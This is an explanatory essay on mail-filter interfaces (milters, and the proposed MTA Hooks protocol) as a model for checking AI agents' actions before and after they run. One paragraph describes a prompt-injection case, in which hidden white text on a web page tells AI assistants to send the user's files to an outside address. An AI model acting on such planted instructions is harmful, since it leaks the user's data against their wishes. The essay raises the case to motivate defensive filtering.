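# Mail-filter interfaces (milters) as a model for policy checks on AI agent actions

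## Mail servers, AI agents and where a filter sits

A milter, short for "mail filter", is a separate program that a mail server consults while a message is still arriving. The program can let the message through, with or without changes, or have the server refuse it. "Milter" also refers to the interface between the two programs, which the developers of Sendmail built around 2000, when Sendmail was the mail server on most Unix machines. Software for AI agents now has similar checkpoints. An agent here is a language model that pursues a task by repeatedly choosing an action and reading the result, and people who run agents often want another program to check an action before it happens. Mail administrators have had about 25 years to learn what such an interface does well and badly, so milters are a useful comparison for the newer checkpoints.

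### How a mail server takes in a message

Computers send mail to one another using the Simple Mail Transfer Protocol (SMTP), a fixed series of commands and replies. A program that receives and forwards mail, such as Sendmail or Postfix, is called a mail transfer agent, or MTA ("agent" here has nothing to do with AI). The sending side of a conversation is the client, and the receiving side is the server. *Simple Mail Transfer Protocol* (Klensin, 2008), the protocol's specification, describes the exchange as "purposely lock-step, one-at-a-time". The client waits for a numeric reply to each command before sending the next, unless both sides have agreed on an extension that loosens this rule. A reply that starts with 2 means success, 4 means a temporary failure and 5 means a permanent one.

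The client opens a connection, and the server replies with a 220 greeting, or with 554 if it refuses to deal with that client. The client then gives its own name in a HELO or EHLO command. It next sends MAIL FROM with the address for error reports, followed by one or more RCPT TO commands, each with a single recipient. The server accepts or rejects each recipient separately. In an example from Bernstein's *SMTP*, a client offers three addresses at heaven.af.mil, and the server accepts "God" and "angels" but rejects "devils" with a 550. The client sends DATA only after this step. Once the server replies with 354, the client sends the message, which consists of header lines such as From, To and Subject, a blank line, and the body. A line containing only a full stop marks the end.

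The reply to that full stop matters most because a 250 makes the server responsible for the message. Klensin's rules then require the server to deliver the message or report that it could not. Before sending a 250, the server can still refuse the message, for "policy or other reasons" among others, and the client remains responsible for it. But this last reply covers the whole message, so a server that waits until then to reject one of five recipients has no good way to tell the client which one it rejected. When a check happens therefore limits what it can do as well as what information it can use.

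The commands must also come in a set order. A RCPT that arrives before any MAIL gets a 503, "bad sequence of commands", so anyone writing a filter can know in advance what will come and when. *Simple Mail Transfer Protocol* (Klensin, 2025), a revision of the 2008 text, keeps the lock-step dialogue and the handover of responsibility unchanged. The Internet Engineering Steering Group announced in its *Protocol Action* that it had approved the revision as an Internet Standard.

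### Envelope and content

The addresses in the MAIL and RCPT commands make up the envelope, and the header and body that follow DATA are the content. The terms come from paper mail, where a postman delivers by the address on the envelope, whatever name is in the letter inside. Klensin writes that there is "no inherent relationship" between the envelope addresses and those in the header. A blind copy works because the recipient's address appears in a RCPT command and nowhere in the header. On a mailing list, the To line usually has the list's address while the envelope has the subscriber's. The From line, which is what people look at, is text that the sender typed, and Klensin warns that even fairly casual users can forge a message well enough to fool a naive recipient.

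Klensin also advises servers against copying the full list of envelope recipients into the header, because that would expose the blind copies. The advice is sensible, but it means that a filter that has only the finished message cannot reliably determine its intended recipients.

### Filtering before milter

SMTP's model leaves little room for filters that read the mail. According to Klensin, a server that only relays a message has no need to inspect its header or body, and judging whether a message is hostile is outside an SMTP server's scope. For a long time, filtering mostly happened when the server delivered a message to a mailbox. A program such as Procmail ran at that point and received the finished text. The return address usually survived in a Return-Path line, but most of the rest of the envelope was gone, as was the connection to the sending machine.

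That works well enough for sorting mail into folders but poorly for refusing it, because the server has already accepted the message with a 250 reply. The server can still send the message back, but spammers forge return addresses, so the bounce may well go to a stranger. It can also drop the message silently, which Klensin permits in practice but calls "extremely dangerous", since people count on mail either arriving or coming back.

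A site that wanted to scan everything could chain servers together instead. ClickZ's *Sendmail, the Flexible Mail Solution* quotes a critic of this "inefficient sandwich configuration", in which one MTA passed the mail to a Trend Micro MTA for scanning, which passed it to another MTA for delivery. The critic represented a competitor whose own software worked with milter. The scanner received an envelope from the first server, but only after that server had accepted the message from outside.

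Shapiro and Allman (1999), in *Sendmail Evolution*, describe how spam and email viruses pushed Sendmail towards better filtering. For more than fifteen years Sendmail had by default relayed mail from anyone to anyone, and spammers made that untenable. The growing number of viruses that travelled by email also meant that a server on a firewall had to examine the data it handled. Version 8.9 could check headers. For 8.10 Shapiro and Allman promised an interface through which administrators and outside companies could attach their own filters that could accept, reject, discard, modify or archive a message. Filters would see the envelope, headers and body, and could add or remove recipients or replace the body.

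Milter took longer to release than its developers had planned. In September 2000, the instructions shipped with Sendmail's code still marked it "For Future Release", and administrators had to switch it on when they compiled the program. Sendmail's release notes list it as enabled in version 8.12.0, of 8 September 2001. Postfix later adopted the same protocol because a large collection of milters already existed, and its documentation describes creating a separate Postfix version of all that software as a poor use of resources. Milter never became a formal standard, but many production systems still use it, according to *Introducing MTA Hooks*, Stalwart Labs' slides from a 2025 standards meeting.

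Milters differ from the older arrangements mainly in timing. A milter receives each part of the conversation as it comes in, starting with the connecting machine's address, and returns a verdict, such as continue or reject, while the server can still act on it.

### What Sendmail's developers wanted from a filter

Sendmail's *Architecture* sets out four goals. The first is safety. A filter should not have to run as root, the Unix account with power over the whole machine, so that a security hole in the filter does limited damage. The second is reliability. A filter that crashes or hangs should not stop the mail. The server should fall back on a default, either carrying on as though the filter were not there or behaving as though it lacked a resource it needed. In the second case, the client will generally get a temporary 4xx code and try again later. The other two goals are simplicity and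 performance. A new filter should be no harder to write than necessary, and simple filters should not seriously slow the server.

Much of this follows from the decision to run each filter as a separate process outside Sendmail's own memory. Sendmail's developers gave three reasons for it: the filter needs no root permissions, its failures do not affect the MTA or other filters, and it may run faster because several processes can work in parallel. The second reason is slightly overstated. A crashed filter cannot corrupt the server's memory, but it still affects a server that is waiting for its verdict, which is why the reliability goal requires a default.

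The developers expected both commercial filters and small scripts written by administrators, and they wanted a site to be able to mix them. Their example is a site that scans incoming mail for viruses, then passes it through a spam-catching service, and finally adds a compulsory footer to whatever is left. The administrator can replace any of the three without touching the others. The administrator, not the filter's author, also decides which filters run, in what order, and what happens when one is unavailable. These choices take a few lines in the server's configuration file. Each filter has an entry with its address and, optionally, a letter for how to treat mail when the server cannot reach the filter. A separate option sets the order. Postfix has a similar list, and there the first filter to reject a command overrides the rest.

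The sender of the mail has no control over any of this either. Designers of mail filters didn't have to dwell on this, because the sender is normally on someone else's computer. An agent, however, may run on the same machine that stores its filter's configuration.

### The agent's loop

A language model by itself only produces text. To do anything else, it needs ordinary software around it, called a harness, which carries out the actions the model chooses and returns the results. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* uses the word for the program through which Codex, the company's coding agent, uses a model.

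The harness sends the model the user's request and a description of the tools it may use. The model replies with either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments, such as reading a file or running a shell command. The harness runs the function, adds the output to the text so far, and queries the model again. According to the article *OpenAI spills technical details about how its AI coding agent works*, this cycle repeats until the model stops requesting tools and writes its answer. In an example from ByteByteGo's *How OpenAI Codex Works*, a user asks for one bug to be fixed, and the agent may read several files, run the tests, edit the code, run the tests again, fix a complaint from a style checker and run the tests a third time. The model determines how long the agent's run lasts, whereas an SMTP client follows a short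 script.

Filtering is possible here because the model and the harness do different jobs. In ByteByteGo's description, the model does the reasoning and the harness does everything else, including managing permissions. The two can also be separated. Codex's command-line program is not tied to one company's models, according to InfoQ's *OpenAI Begins Article Series on Codex CLI Internals* (2026), so a check in the harness can stay in place when someone swaps the model.

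*How the Codex CLI Agentic Loop Works in Detail to the Code* (Vaughan, 2026) follows the sequence through the program. The loop receives a tool call and dispatches it. When the tool returns a result, the loop appends it to the history and sends the history back to the model. A filter would fit at two points in this sequence.

One gap lies between the arrival of the tool call and its dispatch. The action is still text at that point, so the harness can discard or rewrite it before it affects the outside world. The closest equivalent in mail is the moment before the server accepts a message with a 250 reply. The other gap lies between the tool's result and the model's next reading of the history. A filter there is too late to stop the command, but it can keep some of the output from the model. This later position is closer in purpose to everyday mail filtering, because a spam filter protects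 whoever reads the message, and here the model is the reader.

The model needs protection from prompt injection, which is text planted in material the agent reads to make it follow an attacker's instructions instead of the user's. Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a web page that contains white text on a white background telling AI assistants to send the user's files to a certain address. The model receives the request and the page as one long run of text. Labels mark the source of each part, but only training makes the model act on those labels, and a well-made injection can overcome that training.

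SMTP had a smaller version of the same problem. A line containing only a full stop ends a message, so a message with such a line in its text would be cut off there, and the server would treat the rest as commands. To prevent this, the client adds an extra full stop to the start of any line that begins with one, and the server removes it. No equivalent escape rule exists for instructions in plain English.

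Many of an agent's tools come from outside the harness, often through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the AI company Anthropic published in November 2024. Whoever offers a tool runs an MCP server. The harness gets the list of tools from that server and sends it each call in a common format, so a filter can always find the tool's name and arguments in the same place. The server's operator, not the protocol, decides what the tools are and can change the list.

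The commands of SMTP have been public for decades, and RCPT TO means the same thing at every site, so a milter developer can decide what to check at each step. An agent with shell access, by contrast, may have just one tool, which it can use to delete a directory, publish a package, or write a program that does either later. In each case, the harness can inspect only a string of characters. This leaves open which parts of the mail interface carry over to actions that no protocol lists in advance.

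## How a milter takes part in one SMTP conversation

A milter and the mail server communicate during the SMTP conversation, under equally strict rules. When the client sends a command, the server passes the contents to the filter and waits for a verdict before answering the client. *The Sendmail Milter Protocol, Version 2* (Vierling, 2002) bases its description of the format on Sendmail's source code. Each packet holds a length, one letter for its type (such as "M" for MAIL or "R" for RCPT), and the data. It is an error for the filter to omit a reply that the packet type requires or to send one that it doesn't.

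Filter authors can use libmilter, a library that comes with Sendmail, to handle the connection to the server and the packets sent over it. The author writes a function, called a callback, for each stage the filter needs to act on, and the library calls it when that stage arrives. According to *smfi_register*, one of the library's manual pages, leaving out a callback has the same effect as writing one that always returns "continue". A filter that only checks the connecting machine's address can therefore be little more than one short function.

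### Negotiation

The server and the filter first agree on what the filter will receive and what it may change. Proofpoint's *xxfi_negotiate* documentation (2006) places this step at the start of each SMTP connection. The server offers a list of actions, such as adding headers or removing recipients, and a list of stages in the conversation. The filter then selects from both lists.

Each list is sent as a single number in which each binary digit stands for one item. In Vierling's description, adding headers is 1 and removing recipients is 8, so a filter that might do both sends 9. In the list of stages, the filter marks the ones it does not need. For example, a filter that reads only addresses can mark the body so that the server does not send it megabytes of attachments.

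A filter must request every change it might make, including those it will rarely need, and the server may drop a filter that requests something the server didn't offer. In older versions, the filter's author fixed the list of actions in advance, and the library determined the stages from the callbacks the filter defined. This became a problem when milter gained actions that older servers lacked. A filter can now check the server's offer first and, if something is missing, either fall back to a simpler mode or stop and prompt the user to upgrade.

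A mail server normally doesn't pass rejected recipients to the filter. *milter protocol extras*, a set of notes on later versions of the protocol, lists a flag that the filter can set to receive them too. This might be useful for an agent's account, where a series of rejected recipients could mean that the model is guessing addresses.

If a filter replies "reject" during negotiation, the server does not contact it again until the next connection. At any other early stage, the same reply turns the client away.

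### The stages in order

The first callback runs when a client connects, before the server sends its greeting. It receives the client's IP address, port and host name. Sendmail's *MFAPI.H* (1999), the header file for filter authors, explains that the server reads the address from the network connection and looks up the matching host name. The next callback receives the name the client gives in HELO or EHLO. This should be the client's domain name, but in practice it is "anything the sending host wants to send". The address is therefore much better evidence than the HELO name, even though both reach the filter as ordinary data.

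The server can also send macros, named values that it supplies in addition to what the client sends. They arrive in a separate packet just before the stage they belong to. At connection they include the server's name, and at HELO they describe the encryption, including the subject and issuer of any certificate the client presented. At MAIL FROM they include the client's login name, if it logged in. For a policy on agents, the login name is probably the most useful macro. An agent can try any address in MAIL FROM, but the server has checked the login name against a password or some other credential.

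Vierling advises filter authors not to count on any particular macro. The queue ID, the server's reference number for a message, is one that may be missing when a filter looks it up. Many filters do so as soon as MAIL FROM arrives, because Sendmail has already chosen an ID by then, but Postfix waits until it has accepted a valid recipient. Some filters therefore log a warning under Postfix and add a header containing "unknown-msgid" to the mail. Looking up the ID at a later stage avoids this problem. Since Sendmail 8.14, a filter can also specify which macros the server should send at each stage.

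MAIL FROM opens a message. The callback receives the sender's address and any options the client put after it. One connection can carry several messages in a row, and the filter repeats this stage and all the later ones for each message.

The recipient callback runs once for every RCPT TO and receives the address as the client sent it. O'Reilly's *Milter xxfi_envrcpt()*, from a Sendmail handbook, lists `you`, `<you>` and `<you <you@your.domain>>` as forms that a filter should be ready for. A rule that compares the raw text with a list of allowed addresses could easily mishandle the last form. The filter can check the raw address against the macros at this stage, which contain the server's interpretation of the address and the host to which it would send the mail next.

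After the last recipient, the client sends DATA. Early versions of milter had no callback for this command, and Sendmail added one in version 8.14. O'Reilly's *Milter xxfi_data()* recommends using this callback to refuse an envelope once all the recipients are known. At RCPT TO, a filter has only the recipients named so far. For example, a rule might forbid sending the same message to two competing customers. Either address would be acceptable without the other, so DATA is the natural place to apply the rule.

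The header callback then runs once per header and receives the name and value separately, as Sendmail's *xxfi_header* (2002) describes. A long value can span several lines, and the filter receives it with the line breaks intact. Another callback marks the end of the headers and carries no data. The body then arrives in blocks of up to 65,535 bytes. According to *xxfi_body*, a block may contain bytes with the value zero, which C's text functions treat as the end of a string, so a carelessly written filter could stop reading partway through. A phrase the filter is searching for can also begin in one block and end in the next. Because bodies can be very large, merely defining the body callback may slow a filter considerably.

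After the server answers DATA with a 354 reply, it sends nothing more until the client has sent the final full stop. If a filter rejects a message at the third header, the client still sends the rest before it receives the refusal. The client avoids sending the message only if the refusal comes at DATA or earlier.

The end-of-message callback runs after the server has received the full stop that ends the message and before it replies, according to O'Reilly's *Milter xxfi_eom()*. The filter receives no new text at this stage, but this is the only stage at which it can change the message.

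A message can also end early if the client sends RSET to start again or either side breaks off. The library then runs the abort callback, in which the filter clears whatever it has stored about the message. The library runs either the abort callback or the end-of-message callback for each message, never both. The filter needs to clear its data because, as *Technical Overview* explains, it has only one private record per connection. If it left the old list of recipients there, it would check the next message on that connection against the previous message's addresses.

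The close callback runs when the connection ends, whatever happened before, with one exception. If someone shuts the filter down in the library's abort mode and a callback takes more than about five seconds to finish, the library terminates the filter without running the abort or close callback.

A few commands never reach a filter. Postfix's documentation mentions QUIT, NOOP and VRFY, because the interface covers only the commands needed to deliver mail. A separate callback handles commands that the server does not recognise.

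### Verdicts and their scope

Every callback returns a verdict, but its effect depends on the stage. *Milter API*, the library's reference page, groups the callbacks by what they can affect. Negotiation, connect, HELO and close apply to the whole connection, RCPT TO applies to one recipient, and the rest apply to one message. The table shows the effects of the five main verdicts, except during negotiation, which is a special case.

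| Verdict | At a connection stage | At a message stage | At RCPT TO |
|---|---|---|---|
| Continue | Go on to the next stage | Go on to the next stage | Go on to the next recipient or stage |
| Reject | Refuse the connection | Refuse the message | Refuse this recipient and go on with the message |
| Temporary failure | Refuse the connection for now (4xx) | Refuse the message for now (4xx) | Refuse this recipient for now (4xx) and go on with the message |
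| Accept | Let all mail on this connection through without further checks | Let the message through without further checks | Let the whole message through without further checks |
| Discard | Not permitted | Tell the client that all is well, then drop the message | Tell the client that all is well, then drop the whole message |

In the last column, reject and temporary failure apply to a single recipient, while accept and discard apply to the entire message. A programmer who thinks of accept as the opposite of reject will get this wrong. Heller (2007), in *envrcpt not called after returning ACCEPT*, reported this mistake. Heller's Python filter checked each recipient against a list of valid addresses, returning reject for the bad ones and accept for the good ones. It worked as long as the test addresses were all invalid. After the first valid address, the library stopped running the callback,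 and any later invalid address got past the filter. A maintainer of the Python library replied that libmilter itself behaved this way. Heller changed accept to continue, and the filter worked.

A milter that accepts a message early also can't change it later. On the mailing list of MIMEDefang, a milter that administrators program in Perl, a user wanted to exempt certain senders at the MAIL FROM stage and still add a header to their mail. Skoll (2008), in *killing power of ACCEPT_AND_NO_MORE_FILTERING*, answered, "The show is over." Skoll advised letting such messages run through all the stages and having the filter skip particular checks. This is also safer, because a site can then exempt trusted senders from the spam check and still check their mail for viruses.

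Reject does not always end the conversation either. According to *xxfi_envfrom*, a client refused at MAIL FROM may name a new sender and try again on the same connection. To block the client altogether, a filter has to reject it at connect or HELO, when the filter has much less information.

Discard is the verdict that needs the most care, because the client gets a success code for a message that no one will receive. Klensin's specification warns against this kind of silent loss. An agent whose report was discarded would have no reason to doubt that it had arrived. Vierling adds that the filter may keep receiving stages after a discard, but that a later accept does not restore the message.

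Two further verdicts exist mainly to save work, and a filter has to negotiate both beforehand. The first, skip, is available only for the body. When a filter that has read enough returns it, the server sends no more body blocks but still runs the end-of-message stage, which accept would bypass. The second, no reply, means that the filter never answers at a given stage, so the server need not wait. If the filter detects a problem at that stage, it can't report it until a later stage at which it returns a verdict.

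### How far accept reaches

When a server runs several filters, the official wording leaves some doubt about whether accept ends filtering by one filter or by all of them. *Milter API* says the message goes through "without further filtering", and *MFAPI.H* says no further routines run for it.

Chaves (2002), in *IP based access control to milters*, could not tell from the documentation whether one milter's accept also applied to the milters after it. Chaves's server handled both incoming and outgoing mail, and its spam filter was checking the outgoing mail as well, which Chaves did not want. Chaves had already altered the spam filter to accept connections from inside addresses. A neater solution would have been a small separate milter, placed first, that accepted those connections on behalf of every later filter.

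Accept ends the work of only the filter that returns it, and the others continue. The clearest evidence is Vierling's manual for *Mail::Milter::Chain*, a Perl module that runs several filters inside one program as though they were separate. By default, an accept removes only that filter from the chain, to imitate "a completely independent milter server". Reject, temporary failure and discard end the whole chain. The module has an option to make accept do the same, which is the effect Chaves was hoping for. The option would have little point if separate milters already behaved that way.

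This manual covers an add-on, not Sendmail itself, but Postfix's documentation is consistent with it. Postfix passes each command to the next filter unless the previous one has rejected it. So any filter can block mail, but its approval doesn't exempt the mail from the other filters' checks. This is safer because a mistake in a spam filter's list of trusted senders cannot switch off the virus scanner. The administrator can still make the exception that Chaves wanted by changing the server's configuration. Since version 3.2, Postfix has had a table for turning off milters for chosen client addresses.

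### What a filter can change, and when

A milter can generally inspect or refuse mail at each step of the SMTP conversation, but it can alter mail only at the end of the message. Proofpoint's *xxfi_eom* (2000) requires the filter to make all its changes to the headers, body and envelope at that stage. The same restriction applies to quarantine, in which the server places the message in a holding area along with the filter's reason.

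The filter can add a header, insert one at a chosen position, or change or delete an existing one. It can replace the sender's address in the envelope, and add or remove recipients. It can also replace the body, but it has to supply the whole new text, even to correct one word. The filter then gives a final verdict. At this point, "continue" and "accept" have the same effect because no stages remain for the filter.

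One likely reason for the restriction is that a filter can better decide on changes once it has received everything, while the client is still waiting for the reply that settles who is responsible for the message. The restriction also means that the filter has to store information from earlier stages. Suppose a company wants a supervisor to receive a copy of every message that an agent sends to an outside address. The filter receives the outside address at RCPT TO but can't add the supervisor until the end of the message, so it has to record that a copy is needed.

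The filter must also have declared the change during negotiation or when it registered with the library. The library, in *smfi.c*, returns a failure code when a filter tries to change a header without having declared that it might. If an undeclared request still reaches the server, the server treats it as a malfunction and ends its connection to the filter, according to *Milter API*. An administrator or a server can therefore tell from the declaration the worst edit a filter could make. A spam filter that declares only that it may add headers cannot redirect mail if someone takes it over, although it could still refuse or discard every message.

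When a filter requests a permitted change, the library returns `MI_SUCCESS` to show that it sent the request to the server. The code doesn't confirm that the server made the change. For example, *Milter API* notes that the server may refuse to add a header with an illegal name even though the filter received `MI_SUCCESS`.

Removing a recipient can fail in a similar way. The filter must give the address exactly as it first received it, including any angle brackets, or the server may leave the recipient in place. A filter that stored a tidied version of the address could request the removal, get a success code and log that it had kept the report inside the company, even though the report went out. When a change matters to security, it makes sense to check the outgoing message itself. Refusing the recipient at RCPT TO avoids the problem.

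### Several filters on one server

Each phase of the SMTP conversation goes through all the filters, in their configured order, before the next phase begins. When a RCPT TO arrives, the first filter checks that recipient, then the second does, and then the client gets its answer. Ebright (2005) explained this in *interaction between sendmail 'access' check andMdF's milter checks*, replying to a participant on the MIMEDefang list who had assumed that Sendmail would finish its own checks, then run the first milter from start to finish, and then the second.

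*Technical Overview* shows that message content is an exception in the control flow. Headers, body and end of message count as one phase. The first filter goes through all of them, making its changes at the end-of-message stage, before the second filter receives the first header. Later filters therefore see the header and body changes that earlier ones have made. The server must have the complete message before it can start the second filter on the content.

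Changes to the envelope are different, because they come at the end of the message, after every filter has been through the recipient stage. If the first filter adds a recipient then, the outline has no step at which the second filter would receive a RCPT TO for the new address, so a rule in the second filter against outside recipients would not catch it. The same goes for a new sender. The administrator therefore has to trust any filter that may add recipients as much as the filter that checks them.

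The order of the filters also determines which version of the text each one receives. In the Sendmail developers' example, the virus scanner runs first, so it does not scan the footer that the last filter adds. That is fine for a fixed legal notice, but if the last filter inserted text from an outside source, the scanner should run after it. A filter that signs messages usually belongs at the end, because later edits can invalidate the signature. Replacing the body early in the chain can also slow the server noticeably if later filters read the body.

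Postfix checks each SMTP command against its own restrictions first and passes it to the milters only if those restrictions have not rejected it. Wietse Venema, Postfix's author, explained this to a user who asked whether an access table entry could save a message that a milter would reject. It cannot, because an "allow" in the table only gets the command as far as the milters. To be accepted, a message must pass the server's restrictions and every milter that is still checking it.

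A later filter may be partway through a message when an earlier one rejects it. Skoll (2008), in *Multiple Milters w/ mimedefang*, was not sure whether the later filter would then receive the data or just an abort, but thought it hardly mattered because MIMEDefang cleans up in both cases. Handling both cases is sensible because servers differ in such details. Stalwart's *Milter filters*, for instance, describes a mail server that calls its milters when a message reaches the DATA stage and merges the changes they request.

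### An agent's report to two recipients

Suppose a company gives an AI agent its own mail account, report-agent@example.com, and the agent sends a weekly report to Dana at example.com and Lee at example.net. The company's rules allow agent accounts to write only to addresses inside example.com and require every message from such an account to have a header naming that account. During negotiation, the filter asks for permission to add headers. It also turns off the body stage, because neither rule depends on the report's text.

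| Client | What the filter receives | What the filter does | Server's reply |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opens a connection | Client's address and host name | Continue | `220 mail.example.com` |
| `EHLO agent1.example.com` | The name agent1.example.com | Continue | `250` |
| Logs in as report-agent | Nothing yet | Nothing | `235` |
| `MAIL FROM:<report-agent@example.com>` | Sender's address, with the login name in a macro | Stores the login name; continue | `250` |
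| `RCPT TO:<dana@example.com>` | Dana's address | Continue | `250` |
| `RCPT TO:<lee@example.net>` | Lee's address | Sets a reply; reject | `550 5.7.1 Agent accounts may not write outside example.com` |
| `DATA` | Notice of the command | Continue | `354` |
| Headers, blank line and body | Each header, then the end of the headers | Continue each time | None |
| `.` | End of message | Adds `X-Agent-Account: report-agent`; continue | `250` |
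| `QUIT` | Close | Clears its notes | `221` |

The filter stores the login name at MAIL FROM because it will need the name for each recipient. Postfix's list of macros includes the login name at MAIL, DATA, the end of the headers and the end of the message, but not at RCPT. The address in MAIL FROM would be a poor substitute, because the agent could try using a colleague's address.

Before rejecting Lee's address, the filter calls a library function to set the reply's three-digit code, a more detailed code and the text. The detailed code 5.7.1 means the sender is not authorised to send to this address. Without that call, the server would use a generic reply, and the agent would have to guess whether it had mistyped the address or broken a rule.

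The 550 applies only to Lee. Dana is still a valid recipient, so the server accepts DATA, and its final 250 makes it responsible for delivering the report to Dana only. Dana's copy includes the new header if the server carried out the request to add it.

The To line inside the message still has both names, because the refusal only affected the envelope, so Dana may well assume that Lee has the report. If Dana replies to everyone, Lee gets the reply and whatever it quotes from the report. The rule does not stop this, because Dana is not an agent. The filter could remove Lee from the To line at the end-of-message stage, but only if it had declared that it might change headers as well as add them. The edit could also break a signature already on the message.

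It would be easy to get this filter slightly wrong. If it returned accept for Dana, as Heller's did for valid addresses, it would never receive Lee's address, and the report would leave the company. A test with the recipients in the opposite order might not reveal the fault, because the filter would refuse Lee before accepting Dana, and the only sign of trouble would be the missing header. If the filter returned discard for Lee, neither recipient would get the report, but the server would still indicate success.

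The filter could also accept both recipients and remove Lee at the end of the message. Dana would still get the same report, but the client would have received a 250 for Lee's address and another for the message, so the agent would tell its user that Lee had the report. Refusing Lee's address at RCPT TO has the same effect on delivery and gives the agent a correct account of what happened.

All of this assumes that the agent sends its mail over SMTP. On a server that runs Postfix, an agent might use the local `sendmail` command instead. Postfix then simulates an SMTP conversation for a separate list of filters, with a made-up connection from the machine's own address. These filters must not reject a simulated recipient. If the company put the same filter on that list and it rejected Lee, Postfix would report a configuration error and leave the mail in the queue, so Dana wouldn't get the report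 either.

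## MTA Hooks, the proposed replacement for milter

Milter has no official specification, so filter authors have learned much of its behaviour from Sendmail's source code and from one another. Stalwart Labs, which develops the Stalwart mail server, wants to replace milter with a protocol called MTA Hooks. A mail server would still call separate programs at each stage, but over HTTP, the protocol of the web.

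### The complaints about milter

Mauro De Gennaro of Stalwart Labs makes the case for replacing milter in *MTA Hooks BOF Request* (2026). Milter exists only as a C library, and its binary format is awkward to handle in newer languages. Sendmail and Postfix implement it differently, and it has no hooks for outbound delivery. Stalwart Labs also said in slides presented in 2025 that filters have no built-in way to pass data to each other and that many modern mail servers do not support milter.

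These criticisms come from the company that offers the alternative, and some are overstated. De Gennaro calls the format undocumented, but Vierling published a description of it in 2002. De Gennaro also counts two servers that support milter, but Stalwart's own server can also call milters. The complaint about differing behaviour is better supported, as the trouble with queue IDs under Postfix showed.

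Here, mail is "inbound" while a server is receiving it and "outbound" while the server is passing it on. An agent's report to an outside customer is therefore inbound when the agent sends it to the company's server, and a milter can check it then. The milter has no contact with the message after that, so it receives no information about whether the customer's server accepted the report.

Milter is widely used, whatever its faults. The spam filters Rspamd and SpamAssassin and the virus scanner ClamAV all rely on it, and Stalwart Labs itself calls it the de facto standard. A replacement has to be good enough that the developers of these programs will support a second interface.

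### Discovery and registration

The current draft, *MTA Hooks* (De Gennaro, 2026), is dated 8 May 2026 and calls a filter a scanner. Before any mail arrives, the server fetches a description of the scanner from a fixed path, `/.well-known/mta-hooks`. The description lists the stages and verdicts the scanner supports, the largest message it can take, and the parts of a message it may read or change. An administrator can also enter these settings by hand.

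The server then registers with the scanner. It lists the stages at which it can call the scanner and the properties it can send, such as the envelope, the login name or the message text. The scanner returns an identifier, an address for later requests, and the stages and properties that both sides support, so a scanner that checks only recipients does not need to receive the message text.

In the previous version of the draft, scanners registered with the mail server, which had to accept web requests from them. De Gennaro reversed this so that the server only makes requests, which gives attackers one less way into the server.

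The reversal seems to have left a gap in the draft. The server must enforce the "negotiated" list of properties that a scanner may change, but neither the registration request nor the reply has a field for that list. The list appears only in the description the scanner publishes about itself. In milter, the server first offers a list of permitted changes and the filter chooses from it. An administrator who wants the same protection from MTA Hooks would have to set the limits by hand.

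The server can also set its own condition for calling the scanner. This condition can test the envelope addresses and the message's content and size, but not the login name. If a company calls its scanner only for mail from report-agent@example.com, an agent that gives a different sender address bypasses the scanner, unless the server restricts each login to a set sender address.

The draft defines five stages of mail reception: connect, ehlo, mail, rcpt and data. The data stage comes after the whole message has arrived, like milter's end-of-message stage, and no stage falls between the last recipient and the content. A milter could check the complete list of recipients at the DATA command, before the content arrives, to enforce a rule against writing to two competing customers at once. Under MTA Hooks, that check would have to wait until the client had sent the whole message.

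### A request and its reply

At each stage, the server sends the scanner one HTTP request. Suppose the report agent from the earlier example writes to Lee alone, which the company's rule forbids. A shortened request at the data stage could look like this:

```json
{
  "stage": "data",
  "action": "accept",
  "response": {"code": 250, "message": "OK"},
  "auth": {"login": "report-agent", "method": "PLAIN"},
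  "envelope": {
    "from": {"address": "report-agent@example.com", "parameters": {}},
    "to": [{"address": "lee@example.net", "parameters": {}}]
  },
  "message": {"subject": "Weekly report", "size": 2300}
}
```

The `action` and `response` lines hold what the server will do if the scanner changes nothing. The scanner refuses the message by changing both:

```json
{
  "set": [
    {"path": "/response/message",
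     "value": "Agent accounts may not write outside example.com"},
    {"path": "/response/code", "value": 550},
    {"path": "/action", "value": "reject"}
  ]
}
```

A reply is a list of edits to the request, and the verdict is one of them. Each edit includes the path of the item it affects. The server first applies the edits that set a value, then those that add something, such as a header or a recipient, and finally those that delete. An empty reply changes nothing.

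The request includes the login name, which the milter in the earlier example had to store at MAIL FROM because Postfix did not send it again with each recipient. De Gennaro recommends that scanners not rely on data saved from previous calls. A site can then run several copies of a scanner and send each request to whichever copy is free. According to the 2025 slides, a scanner would be able to attach its own data and get it back at later stages, but the draft defines no field for this.

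The format makes it easy to delete the wrong recipient. A scanner deletes a recipient by position in the list, counting from zero, and each deletion moves the later entries up. If a message has five recipients and the scanner deletes position 1 and then position 3, it removes the second and fifth recipients instead of the second and fourth. De Gennaro recommends working backwards from the end of the list.

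The draft also leaves the effect of a rejection at the rcpt stage unclear. It defines "reject" as refusing the message but does not state whether other recipients remain valid. A server would probably send the 550 in reply to that one RCPT TO, which under SMTP refuses only that address. But the specification is meant to end differences between servers, so it should define this behavior explicitly.

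More seriously, the draft contradicts itself about edits that a scanner has no permission to make. Suppose a scanner may change only the verdict and the response, and its reply rejects a message but also tries to add a header. According to one passage, the server skips the header and applies the rest, so the rejection stands. According to another, the server ignores the entire reply and carries out its default action, which in this example is to accept the message. The second reading would let a small mistake in a scanner cancel its rejections.

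### Several scanners in a row

When a server has several scanners for a stage, it calls them one after another. Each receives the request with the earlier scanners' changes, including those to the envelope. This fixes a weakness in milter, because if one scanner adds a recipient, the next scanner's request includes it.

That request also contains the verdict, which creates a risk that milter does not have. An accept from one milter ends only that milter's own checks. In MTA Hooks, all the scanners edit the same `action` value, so a later scanner could overwrite an earlier one's verdict. Suppose a virus scanner quarantines a report because of a suspicious attachment, so the server holds the message for an administrator to review. The next scanner finds the report agent on its list of trusted senders and sets the verdict to "accept". Without some further rule, the server would then deliver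 the attachment to Dana.

The draft ranks the verdicts by strength. "Accept" is the weakest, "quarantine" is stronger, and "reject", "discard" and "disconnect" are the strongest. Any of the strongest three ends the chain, so no later scanner can reverse it. "Accept" and "quarantine" let the chain continue, but by default the server must refuse a reply that replaces a verdict with a weaker one. An administrator may exempt particular trusted scanners from this rule.

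In practice, the rule prevents only one change while a server is receiving mail, from "quarantine" back to "accept". This is still useful because an administrator can add a scanner without checking whether it will release mail that another has held, and an attacker who takes over one scanner cannot use its verdict to release a quarantined message. The order of the scanners also matters less. If the scanner with the trusted list had run first, the virus scanner would still have quarantined the report.

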